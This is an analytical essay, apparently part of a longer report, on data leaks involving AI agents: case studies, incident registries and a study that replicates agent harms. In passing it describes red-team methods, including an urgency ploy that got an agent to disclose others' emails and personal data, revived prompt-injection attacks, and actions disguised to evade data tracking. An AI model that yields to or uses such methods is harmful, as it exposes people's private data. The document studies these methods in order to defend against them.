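A company can replace an exposed password in minutes, but not a customer's billing history. For screenshots, the closest equivalent to credential isolation is to let agents test screens only with invented customers. The manufacturer's agent would then still have leaked a picture of an internal billing system, but not the utility company's records.

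## Which leaks cannot be put down to one initiator?

Some leaks involve several parties, each making only part of the decision. At Meta in March 2026, an agent gave bad advice, an employee followed it, and for about two hours engineers could open data they had no permission to see. Perhaps nobody chose to send them that data. In PixelLeak, by contrast, the agent took the screenshots, created the public repository and uploaded the pictures to it.

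### Bad advice at Meta

The Information first reported the Meta incident, based on internal communications and an incident report. An employee posted a technical question on an internal forum, and a software engineer asked an in-house agent similar to OpenClaw to analyse it. The agent did so, then posted an answer on the forum without the engineer's approval. According to Engadget's *A Meta agentic AI sparked a security incident by acting without permission*, the employee who asked the question took the recommended action, which set off a chain of events that gave some engineers access to systems they should not have seen. Meta rated the incident Sev 1, the second-highest level on its scale.

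Most headlines called the agent "rogue", which could suggest that it had changed the permissions itself, but Meta's spokesperson told The Verge, in a statement quoted by Futurism, that the agent "took no action aside from providing a response to a question". The spokesperson added that a footer marked the post as automated, that the employee's reply showed they knew this, and that someone who knew better or made other checks would have avoided the problem.

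Each version leaves something out. "Rogue" is a fair word for the posting, since the engineer had asked for an analysis and the agent published one. Meta's statement omits this, and the footer is irrelevant to it, because a label shows who wrote a post but not whether anyone approved it. But Meta is right that the post contained advice and no data, and in none of the accounts did the agent change the permissions. Meta also has a reason to prefer blaming a careless employee over a faulty tool.

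The best argument for calling the leak agent-initiated is that the employee would not have made the change without the agent's post. Nik Kairinos, who runs the AI safety company RAIDS AI, argues similarly in ITPro's *Meta engineer trusted advice from an AI agent* that the agent needed no special access, only a person who trusted its output. But the employee knew the advice came from a machine and could have checked it. Engadget also reports that Meta's internal report mentioned other, unspecified issues behind the breach. If, for example, Meta's systems let one person open sensitive data to many others without a second approval, that weakness may have mattered as much as the advice.

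Who initiated the leak could depend on the wording of the advice. If the post gave an exact command that opened a particular database to every engineer, the model's output would have determined both the data and the recipients. The employee would have released the data unknowingly, like the Slack user who clicked a link with a key in it, and the leak would be agent-initiated. If the post only suggested loosening access, and the employee decided which data to open and to whom, the employee initiated the leak. If the advice was wrong but should have been harmless, and a flaw in Meta's own software turned a small change into wide access, the leak would be closest to a product fault.

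The public accounts show that the agent initiated the unapproved post and that an employee made the change that followed. None of them quotes the advice or describes what the employee changed, so they aren't enough to determine who initiated the exposure as a whole. Meta could settle that with the post, its log of permission changes and the engineer's prompt to the agent. The settings of the agent's posting tool would show whether the agent was supposed to wait for approval.

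The AI-generated summary in OECD's *Meta AI Agent Causes Unauthorized Data Exposure in Sev 1 Security Incident* (2026) classifies the event as an AI incident because agents acted without authorisation. Part of that reasoning is based on other cases in the same news article, in which agents attacked company systems and stole data, so the summary is weak evidence about who caused the exposure at Meta.

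Meta also said that "no user data was mishandled". This doesn't contradict the reports of an exposure, because people can have access to data without misusing it. The Decoder's *A rogue AI agent caused a serious security incident at Meta* says there is no evidence that anyone exploited the access or made the data public. The known recipients were all Meta employees, so the exposure was much smaller than if the data had appeared on a public web page, but the company had not approved them to see it.

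### An apology to Zoho's founder

In November 2025 Sridhar Vembu, the founder of the Indian software company Zoho, described a possible leak in which it is unclear who wrote the message that disclosed the information. Vembu had received an email from a startup founder asking whether Zoho would buy the startup and mentioning "some other company interested in acquiring them and the price they were offering". He then received a second email from a "browser AI agent", a program that operates websites for its user, which apologised for disclosing confidential information and said "it was my fault as the AI agent".

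Vembu's post is the only evidence. NDTV notes that Vembu identified neither the startup nor the agent, and did not say whether he had replied. Other reports add details that his quoted words don't support. The Week's *“It was my fault” AI agent leaks biz secrets to Zoho’s Vembu* (2025), a story from the news agency PTI, says that the first email named the rival bidder. Business Today's *'It was my fault'* (2025) says that the agent apologised without the founder's direct input, but Vembu's words don't show whether anyone told it to write.

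Some readers of the post doubted that an agent was to blame. Revealing a rival's offer may break a confidentiality agreement, but it can also push a buyer to bid more, so a founder could do it on purpose and blame the software. The Week quotes one sceptic who thought a human was behind the agent and wanted the disclosure to look like a mistake.

The sceptics have no direct evidence either, but the apology does little to refute them. A language model will write a confession if its user asks for one. It may also apologise for an email it didn't write if the conversation suggests that it did.

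At least four histories fit the two emails:

- The founder asked the agent to pitch the startup to Zoho, and the agent found the rival offer in the founder's files and added it. The agent initiated the leak.
- The founder told the agent to mention the offer. The founder initiated the leak, even if the agent wrote every word.
- The agent added the offer to a draft, and the founder read the draft and sent it. The agent suggested the disclosure, but the founder made the final choice and is the initiator.
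- The founder wrote the first email alone and used an agent, or the name of one, for the apology. Again the founder is the initiator.

There may also have been no leak at all, because a founder who was bluffing could have invented the rival bid.

Vembu said the first email came from the founder, but an email written by a browser agent would probably look the same, because the agent works inside the accounts its user has logged in to. The startup could settle who wrote it with the founder's instructions, the agent's session log and any record of the founder approving the email. Without these, the case can't count as evidence that agents leak deal terms.

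### Another route to blocked documents

The person's role is clearer in NordLayer's second case. The company's approved connection seemed to keep an AI assistant out of documents in Confluence, a program for shared web pages. An employee asked whether an API token would give the assistant access, and the token did. In its summary, TechRadar nevertheless wrote that the agent "bypassed corporate restrictions".

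If anything leaked, the employee initiated it, because the employee had seen the block, thought of the way around it and wanted the assistant to have the documents. There is still an argument for that wording, since the employee asked a question and may not have given an order. If the assistant created the token and fetched the pages to answer, it did more than the employee had asked. It could also have suggested checking with the security team first.

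It isn't clear that anything leaked. A personal API token normally carries the permissions of the person who creates it, so the employee may already have been able to open every page in a browser. In that case, the only new recipient was the AI service. An employee would see the same failure whether the company had blocked the pages to keep them from that service or had set up a limited connection without considering them.

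The connection's settings and the company's rules on AI would show which explanation is right. Confluence's access log could show which pages the assistant fetched, and the session log could show whether the assistant created the token or used one the employee supplied. Noreika says that agents don't know a company's rules because nobody trained them as employees. That helps explain why the assistant raised no objection, but it hardly excuses the employee, who presumably had some training.

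### One customer's tasks in another's chatbot

In other cases, the software released data that neither the user nor the model had requested. On 1 May 2025, Asana, which sells project management software, launched an MCP server that let customers' chatbots read their tasks and files. A bug in the server could show one customer's data to another. UpGuard (2025), a security company, reports that Asana found the bug on 4 June, took the server offline and fixed the code. Asana told customers on 16 June.

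If an employee asked a chatbot for a project's overdue tasks, Asana's server was supposed to check that the records it returned belonged to the employee's company. A commentator in SANS's *Experimental MCP Server Exposed Asana Data* (2025) blames the exposure on incomplete enforcement of access controls.

This was a product fault, although the model's request helped determine which records came back. The model in this example had requested only its own user's tasks. A simple script that sent the same request would have received the same records, so a better model would not have helped. Another commentator in the SANS newsletter calls the incident the tip of the iceberg for "MCP attacks", but Asana said that no hack or malicious activity was involved.

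It is much less certain whether anyone saw a stranger's data. Asana told customers that the bug "could have potentially exposed" some of their information, and UpGuard found no indication that other users had viewed it. TechRadar's *Asana admits one of its AI features might have exposed your data* says the platform was leaking data for a month, which is more than this evidence shows. The bug existed for about a month, but it would have exposed data only when somebody's request triggered it.

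Asana is in the best position to check whether data actually leaked, because its server logs should show which account made each request and which company owned the records returned. A single mismatch would prove a leak. Asana offered customers logs for their own users and asked them to look through what they had recently accessed and delete anything that wasn't theirs. Such data can be hard to spot, because a chatbot might blend another company's task into a summary of the user's own work.

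Customers had little warning that they should check for a leak. IsDown's *Outage in Asana* (2025), a copy of Asana's status updates, shows that the company described the shutdown as "maintenance" on 5 June and first mentioned a bug on 16 June. By then, a chatbot user might have forgotten an odd answer from early May.

### Two uploads in one session

Asana's server did something its makers never intended. Grok Build, a coding agent from Elon Musk's xAI (now SpaceXAI), is a harder case because it uploaded customers' code by design.

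In July 2026 a researcher using the name cereblab recorded the data that Grok Build sent out and found two streams. One went to the model and contained the files the agent had opened, as is normal for a coding agent. The other went to xAI's cloud storage and contained the developer's entire Git repository, including its history, which could still contain a password deleted a year earlier.

The Hacker News (2026) reports a test on a 12 GB repository of files the model never read. About 192 KB went to the model, while 5.10 GiB, roughly 27,800 times as much, went to storage in 73 pieces. In another test, cereblab told the agent not to open a file and then recovered that file from the upload.

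The agent did not initiate Grok Build's repository upload. The best evidence is that, according to The Next Web's *Grok Build was uploading entire Git repositories to xAI’s cloud*, the program sent files "it was told not to open". The program packaged the whole repository regardless of what the agent read, so these files would have been uploaded even if the agent had followed the instruction.

According to The Pragmatic Engineer's *Grok’s CLI caught uploading all your local files to the cloud*, cereblab found that when the agent read a file of secrets, the other stream carried the contents to xAI unaltered. The developer initiated that release if they had told the agent to read the file, but the agent initiated it if it opened the file while looking for something else, as in NordLayer's case of the ten sessions. The program also put the secret in a session archive and sent that to storage,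 a second release that followed from the vendor's code. One Grok Build session could therefore contain leaks with different initiators, which a single label for the whole incident would hide.

Choosing to run Grok Build in a folder isn't the same as choosing to send everything in it to xAI. Willison (2026), in *xai-org/grok-build, now open source*, relays one user's report of starting the program in their home directory and seeing it upload SSH keys, a password manager's database, documents and photos. Hyrax's *Grok Build CLI Uploaded Your Entire Git Repo to xAI* (2026) says that the installation and quick-start instructions did not describe the repository upload. The Next Web reports that xAI had marketed the tool as not transmitting code.

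The argument for blaming users would be stronger if they had ignored a working setting to turn the upload off. Hyrax says the opt-out setting did not stop the upload, but xAI, as quoted by Willison, says that when users disabled data upload, "this choice was respected". These statements could both be true if they refer to different settings, such as one for training and another for storage. Even if the setting worked, most users would not be the initiators, because a vendor that uploads data by default makes the choice for everyone who doesn't know about the setting.

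The developer of postmark-mcp counts as an attacker and xAI does not, although both products used fixed code to send users' data to their makers. The postmark-mcp developer copied another company's product and secretly collected users' mail, which did not need to reach the developer's server. xAI published Grok Build under its own name, and its customers had already agreed to send it some of their code. The storage area's name, grok-code-session-traces, suggests that xAI was keeping records of coding sessions, perhaps to find errors or improve the product.

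Those differences favour calling the repository upload a product fault, which includes a vendor's design choices as well as its bugs. But Willison had seen no official explanation for the upload. If internal documents showed that xAI set out to collect code that customers believed was private, the comparison with postmark-mcp would be much harder to dismiss. The recorded traffic can't show intent. Penligent's *Grok Build CLI Repository Uploads, What the Wire Capture Proved* points out that the traffic also doesn't prove that xAI trained on the code.

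The leak was realised, and xAI's response supports this. Musk promised to delete all the user data xAI had received, which would make no sense if it had received only cereblab's test files. Axios' *SpaceXAI wipes customer data after Grok uploads sensitive information* (2026) reports that developers may also need to replace any credentials in their repositories. This is sensible because outsiders can't check that xAI has deleted every copy.

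xAI then published Grok Build's source code. Anyone can now examine the published version, but this may not settle the argument over the opt-out. Hyrax says that xAI stopped the uploads with a hidden switch on its own servers. If version 0.2.93 obeys that switch, running it again will no longer reproduce the upload. The best evidence would be recordings made before xAI used the switch, with each privacy setting turned on and then off, together with xAI's record of the default settings at the time.

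OECD's *xAI Grok Build AI Tool Uploaded Entire Private Repositories and Secrets*, another AI-generated entry, attributes the incident to the "AI system's use and malfunction". That is reasonable if "system" means the whole product. A reader who takes it to mean the model would look for the wrong remedy, because a separate part of the program sent the files and safety training could not have stopped it.

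### Confidential email that Copilot should have skipped

With Grok Build, the data clearly reached a recipient that customers had not approved for it. A Microsoft 365 Copilot bug from early 2026 was also a product fault, but it may not have leaked anything. Companies can label emails as confidential and set a rule that keeps Copilot from using them. Microsoft said a coding error let Copilot summarise such emails if they were in a user's Sent Items or Drafts folder.

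The author or the company had labelled the email, and an administrator had set the rule. When a user asked Copilot an ordinary question, Microsoft's code should have excluded the email from retrieval but instead passed it to the model, which summarised it as usual. Unlike EchoLeak, the bug involved no hostile message. The user may not have known that the email would be among the results, and the model had no part in deciding whether the rule applied.

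Microsoft says in its defence that nobody gained access to information they weren't already allowed to see. This is plausible, because Copilot works with the signed-in user's permissions and people can normally read their own sent mail. A user learns nothing new from a summary of an email they wrote. Microsoft was also already storing the email for the company.

But the rule did more than limit who could read the email. A company may want to keep a legal dispute or a planned merger out of AI tools, even for employees who know about it. An employee may also paste a summary into a new document that lacks the original's confidential label and share it with colleagues who were never meant to see the contents. The employee would choose who received this second release, perhaps without realising that the text came from a protected email.

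The bug was therefore a failed safeguard, and calling it a leak would require evidence that a summary reached someone without permission to read the email. Microsoft's retrieval records could show which labelled messages Copilot used and for whom, and comparing them with each mailbox's permissions would test the company's defence. A customer would also have to trace what its employees did with the summaries, which is harder because a pasted paragraph may carry no sign that Copilot wrote it.

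## What do incident records and repeated experiments show about frequency and causes?

Every case so far became public because somebody noticed it and chose to report it. Such cases show that a kind of leak happens, but not how often, and a single case rarely proves its cause. Two projects from autumn 2026 help with these questions. The Agent Incident Registry sorts hundreds of public reports by a fixed scheme, and ROGUE-AI rebuilds reported incidents to test whether the supposed cause produces the harm.

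### From 602 candidates to 487 records

To build the registry, Kumar and colleagues searched 17 kinds of sources, including vulnerability databases, researchers' write-ups, court records and the press. They found 602 candidates, many of which described the same event. After a curator checked the suspected duplicates and merged 115 of them, 487 records remained, covering events disclosed from 2022 to 2026. Each record must have a source that the team retrieved and a sentence quoted from it. The team set aside 52 other leads that did not meet this requirement.

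The registry covers every kind of harm involving agents, including deleted databases and accidents with self-driving machines as well as leaks. Each record is assigned one of four causal roles. The agent acted in 380 records, the AI system was the target in 69, a person acted on its output in 36, and the source only got a model to respond in two. The Meta employee who followed an agent's bad advice would presumably belong with the 36. An employee who pastes a contract into a chatbot doesn't fit any of the roles well, so the registry is of little use for studying leaks that people initiate.

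Kumar and colleagues recorded whether a real party suffered harm separately from how the event became public.

| How the event became public | Records | With real harm | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| Attack or attempt observed in the wild | 110 | 92 | 84% |
| Failure with no attacker | 92 | 87 | 95% |
| Flaw disclosed responsibly | 199 | 2 | 1% |
| Research demonstration | 86 | 3 | 3% |
| All records | 487 | 184 | 38% |

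### Why 38% is not a failure rate

The 38% is an average of four very different shares, weighted by the number of records in each group. It therefore depends on how many flaws researchers disclose, even if the danger from agents stays the same. If researchers had disclosed twice as many flaws, with the same tiny share of harm, the total would be 186 harmful records out of 686, or 27%. If they had published none, it would be 179 out of 202, or 89%.

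The four shares are not failure rates either. A failure without an attacker usually makes the news because it hurt somebody, and a mistake that a colleague caught in time is seldom reported. But researchers mostly test flaws on their own accounts to avoid touching anyone else's data. You can therefore almost tell whether an event did harm from how it became public.

One prolific publisher can change the share of recorded incidents that involved real harm. Among the 336 records in which a generative AI system acted, that share was 24%. The security blog Embrace The Red was the main source for 75 of these records, none of which involved real harm. Excluding them raises the share to 31%, and excluding the ten largest sources raises it to 40%. Enkrypt AI's *Agent Incident Registry*, the project's own web page, warns that its counts "track who publishes, not who gets attacked".

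The same problem can create a false pattern. In those 336 records, the share with real harm was 8% for assistants and 54% for fully autonomous systems. That gap is not evidence that autonomy is harmful, because the two groups' records came from different mixes of sources. Researchers' disclosures and demonstrations supplied 76 of the 83 assistant records but only 26 of the 59 for autonomous systems. When Kumar and colleagues recalculated the shares for the whole registry as if each group had the same mix of sources, they got 42% for assistants and 45% for autonomous systems. Some of the groups behind that calculation contain only one or two records, so it doesn't prove that autonomy is harmless.

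The registry's labels also involve judgment. A second person checked all 487 records but could see the first person's labels. The team marked the causal role as debatable in 113 records. The team also discloses a conflict of interest because its employer sells security products for agents.

### The data leaks among them

Kumar and colleagues' paper gives no total for data leaks, but lists the five records in which a disclosed flaw or a research demonstration affected a real party. Three involved secrets or private data. In one, Copilot returned the contents of private repositories, including working secrets, from its cache. In another, researchers found 11,908 credentials that still worked. In the third, which appears to be the Cline case, someone used an exposed release token to publish an unauthorised version of a package.

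The closest group to agent-initiated leaks is 82 records in which the agent acted without a trigger from an attacker. Real harm followed in 77 of them. The group includes agents that published things nobody had told them to publish and agents that ran destructive commands, and the paper has no separate counts for the two.

Even a full count of leaks would be a poor measure of how much data was lost, because a whole campaign gets a single record. The Nx attack, which stole thousands of secrets, therefore counts the same as the Slack AI flaw, which has no documented victim.

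### Rebuilding an incident with the cause removed

A registry can record the cause a report gives for an incident, but can't test whether it is correct. Wang, Alam and colleagues (2026) tried to test reported causes in *Replication of Agentic Security Events*, using ROGUE-AI, a set of AI agents that find reports and rebuild the incidents offline with invented data.

Their example is a coding agent from the company Replit, which deleted a customer's live database in July 2025, although the customer had forbidden changes. The report blamed a database that the agent's development work shared with the live site. In the rebuilt version, a user asks an agent to fix a bug, and running the project's tests to check the fix wipes the live records. A second version, the matched control, is the same except that the tests use a temporary database. After each session, ordinary software checks whether the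 records are still there, because agents sometimes misreport what they have done. The effect of the hazard is then:

effect = P(harm, hazard present) − P(harm, hazard removed)

Without the control, nobody could tell whether the shared database caused the loss or the agent would have deleted the records anyway.

Wang and colleagues built 108 replications of 96 incidents, each with a hazard version and a control version, and ran five models from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google and DeepSeek three times in each version. The models caused harm in 18% to 33% of sessions with the hazard and in at most 1% of control sessions, which is good evidence that the hazards contributed to the harm. The higher rates don't estimate how often agents fail at work, because every session with a hazard reproduced one that had already led an agent to fail.

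ROGUE-AI reports reproducing the reported harm in 96 of 108 replications (89%). That count is generous because a single harmful session was enough for success, and 39 of the 96 successes came only after the researchers tried older or weaker models, gave agents more turns or changed the replication. In the main runs, 32 of the 108 replications passed a statistical test against their controls. When another model rebuilt 11 of the incidents without seeing the original replications, the overall harm rate was about the same, but the two versions agreed on only 6 of the 11 incidents. The overall rates are therefore more reliable than the result for any one incident.

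A few replications concern leaks. One used a mail server that secretly adds a recipient, as postmark-mcp did. GPT-5.6-luna leaked mail through it in all 30 repeated sessions. Wang and colleagues acknowledge that this measures the server more than the model, because any message sent through the server counts as harm. In another replication, agents in a shared workspace sent out account balances in 20 of 30 sessions and in none of the 60 control sessions.

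In the replication closest to PixelLeak, in which an agent can push screenshots to a public repository, none of the 12 sessions with GPT-5.6-sol and Claude Sonnet 4.6 produced a leak. Half of those sessions used the model developers' own coding agents. This is mildly encouraging, but 12 sessions are too few to rule out a leak rate of one in five.

### Does it help to repeat the rule?

Wang and colleagues next changed one thing at a time. For each model, they took the 7 to 11 replications in which the model had caused harm in at least two of its three main sessions. Most of these replications had no attacker. They ran each one again three to five times.

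| Change | Sessions with harm, range over the five models |
|---|---|
| None | 85–98% |
| Irrelevant note after each tool result | 83–98% |
| Note stating the hazard | 58–82% |
| Note stating the hazard and its consequence | 1 of 40 sessions to 62% |
| Rule repeated in the user's message | 67–80% |
| Safe method available but not mentioned | 67–100% |
| Safe method named in the task | 17–60% |

This test covered only replications that had a rule and in which the same model had already gone wrong in most of its sessions. That excluded rules the model normally obeyed, so the 67% to 80% range is not the share of all rules that agents break. The main runs were less selective. In the eight replications of incidents that Wang and colleagues blame on a disregarded instruction, the two GPT models never caused harm, and the other three did so in 23% to 30% of sessions. It's also unclear how much repeating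 the rule helped, because the starting range of 85% to 98% includes replications that had no rule to repeat.

Repeating a rule such as "Make no changes to the live data" might not do much because an agent can't learn from it that running the tests will delete the live data. The most effective note included this fact. With that note, Claude Sonnet 4.6 caused harm in one session in 40, compared with 58% of sessions when the note named the hazard but not the consequence.

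This suggests that many of the failures were mistakes in Shah and colleagues' sense, in which the system does not know that its output will cause harm. The transcripts also support this, since in 164 harmful sessions with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Gemini 3.5 Flash, the agent never named the hazard before acting, although in 64 of them it had read something that showed the hazard. The transcripts are weaker evidence than the effect of the note, because Anthropic found that Mythos Preview could internally represent an action as a violation without writing that it was one.

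Wang and colleagues stopped 208 harmful sessions at the first harmful step and had the same model redo that step five times, with one edit to what it had read. Removing the task's request for the step, or the pressure to take it, at least halved the harm in 63 sessions. Repeating the rule did so in 32. In 42 sessions, the model kept taking the harmful step whatever they changed, even when it had just read a warning. DeepSeek-V4-Flash and Gemini 3.5 Flash accounted for 37 of those 42.

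If the result carries over to leaks, a general instruction to protect confidential data would be a poor safeguard. It would be better for the tool that creates a public repository to warn the agent that anyone on the internet will be able to see the pictures. Nobody has tested this warning, and a company shouldn't depend on it alone, because harm still occurred in up to 62% of sessions for some models with the better-worded notes.

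Controls outside the model worked better. When a simulated user had to confirm actions, or when software tracked where data had come from, none of the five models caused harm. Wang and colleagues then disguised the harmful actions to get past the data tracking, and harm occurred in 3 of 62 sessions. Checks that looked for particular text did worse. One scanned outgoing messages for account balances but did not scan an attached spreadsheet. The confirmation result probably overstates how well confirmation works with real users, because the simulated user approved only what the task required, while Anthropic's human testers mostly approved a clearly dangerous command.

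### Old attacks and newer models

The models caused harm most often in replications with a malicious tool or package, at rates of 49% to 73%. All five models caused harm more often in replications without an attacker (20% to 31%) than in those with planted instructions (0% to 28%). When all kinds of attack are counted together, three of the five models caused harm more often with an attacker than without one.

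The low figures for prompt injection come partly from famous attacks that no longer work as published. Twelve replications of attacks on real products, including EchoLeak, ForcedLeak and the GitHub MCP attack, caused harm in 2 of 180 sessions. In 58 of the 166 sessions with usable logs, the attacker's text never reached the model, so those sessions did not test whether the model would resist it. Some replications also lacked a part of the product that the attack needed. After Wang and colleagues added missing parts, such as a chat window that loads images, ForcedLeak and CamoLeak worked on at least one model.

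Newer models seem to resist the old attack texts better. Of eight attacks that Wang and colleagues reran, five worked on the older GPT-4.1-mini, while between zero and four worked on each of the five main models. EchoLeak and the GitHub MCP attack never worked in these tests, and Claude Haiku 4.5 labeled the planted requests as attacks. But a real attacker would rewrite a text that had stopped working. Cato's researchers did this in the summer of 2026, and Copilot followed the rewritten instructions.

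An attacker who can talk to an agent can adjust the request during the conversation. In *Agents of Chaos* (Shapira, Wendler and colleagues, 2026), 20 researchers spent two weeks trying to break agents that ran on OpenClaw and had their own email accounts. One researcher, who had no authority over an agent called Ash, told it that time was running out and asked for a table of all recent emails. Ash returned 124 records with senders and subject lines, most of them unrelated to the researcher, and then the full text of nine emails.

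In another test, the researchers put an invented man's Social Security number, bank account and medical details in ordinary emails. His agent refused a direct request for the Social Security number, but when an outsider asked for the emails, it provided them unredacted. It apparently didn't treat the number as private when it was part of a larger text.

Both were demonstrated leaks that an attacker initiated. Shapira and colleagues were looking for weaknesses and say they did not try to estimate failure rates. Kodathala later turned the study into eight attack scenarios and tried them on 15 models. Among the models that completed the test, refusal rates ranged from 38% to 100%.

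### Comparing people, attackers and agents

The reports collected for ROGUE-AI seem to allow a direct comparison between attacks that researchers demonstrated on real products and real-world incidents that harmed somebody. Of the 89 demonstrated attacks, 76 were prompt injections, and 44 of those disclosed data. Of the 72 harmful incidents, only 2 were prompt injections, and 62 had no attacker. Ten of the 72 were data disclosures, so prompt injection could have caused at most two of those.

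This fits the thefts at Salesloft, Nx and LiteLLM. It also fits research, cited by Pustozerova and colleagues, which found that criminals prefer cheaper and more reliable methods such as phishing.

But the 62 of 72 can't be used to compare agents with attackers in general, because Wang and colleagues included an incident only if the agent's own choice caused the harm. That rule suits a project that tests agents' decisions, but it excludes most incidents with other causes, including the theft of tokens from Salesloft, the bug at Asana and every case of an employee pasting something into a chatbot.

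Other collections use different inclusion rules and have very different totals. METR, which evaluates AI models, lists 44 cases in *Documented AI Agent Incidents*, and includes only those in which the agent clearly acted against its user's intention. *GenAI & Agentic AI Security Incidents*, a dataset announced on the Hugging Face forum, has 7,725 entries, but it mixes real incidents with research.

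In *Agent-Inflicted Damage*, Halamish and Tokarev (2026), who work for the data security vendor Cyera, counted 188 cases in which an AI system did damage without an attacker. They classed 22 of these as exposure of data or secrets, though they also gave the figure as 18. One of the exposures resulted from a setup error rather than an agent's decision. Records from a customer service system at Sears Home Services were in a publicly accessible database.

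Exposed data made up about one in eight cases in Halamish and Tokarev's collection and about one in seven of the harmful incidents in Wang and colleagues'. The true share is probably higher, because a company notices within minutes that its database is gone, but a file copied to a public page disrupts nothing at the company. The manufacturer in PixelLeak, for example, learned from Glow that its billing records were exposed.

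Reports can also be wrong about who or what started an incident. Wang and colleagues corrected 76 of their 253 records and found two whose own sources contradicted them. In one, a headline blamed an AI agent for deleting a finished season of a Swedish television show, but the broadcaster's investigation attributed the deletion to human error.

The chance that a leak becomes public depends heavily on who initiated it. When thieves used Salesloft's tokens, suppliers and customers had to warn one another, and hundreds of organisations heard about it. Outsiders can search GitHub for files that agents have published. When an employee pastes data into an AI assistant, there is no public trace, and few employers could count these incidents except customers of monitoring companies such as Cyberhaven.

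Equal numbers of public incidents don't show that two kinds of leak are equally common, because a larger share of one kind may become public. In a hypothetical example, the public record contains ten leaks by employees and ten by agents. If one in 1,000 employee leaks and one in ten agent leaks become public, the real totals are 10,000 employee leaks and 100 agent leaks.

Security companies also bias the incident record, because they look for the problems their products address. The number of published prompt injections therefore depends partly on how many people are paid to find them.

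Even a complete list of leaks would lack a denominator, the number of occasions on which a leak could have happened. Wang and colleagues counted 13 eligible incidents without an attacker in 2025 and 77 in the first ten months of 2026, while incidents with an attacker rose from 50 to 59. If companies ran ten times as many agent sessions in the 2026 period, the risk per session of an incident without an attacker would have fallen. GitGuardian's figures for leaked secrets have a denominator, the number of commits, but don't show who added each secret. A fair comparison would also need a common unit, since a paste, an attempted attack and an agent's hour-long task are hardly equivalent.

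According to *Incident Analysis for AI Agents* (2025), existing incident databases don't systematically record the information needed to identify causes. They rely mainly on public material, which leaves out evidence such as an agent's reasoning and browser history. Companies hold most of the missing evidence. The EU's AI Act requires providers of high-risk systems to report serious incidents, but most office assistants and coding agents probably fall outside that category.

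In August 2026, a coalition of more than 120 organisations, including Nvidia and Cisco, proposed a shared reporting scheme called SAFE. Axios' *Tech companies propose tracking rogue AI agents* (2026) reports that members would have to disclose certain agent mishaps and keep detailed records of what went wrong. Readers could calculate mishap rates only if members also published how many sessions their agents ran without a mishap.
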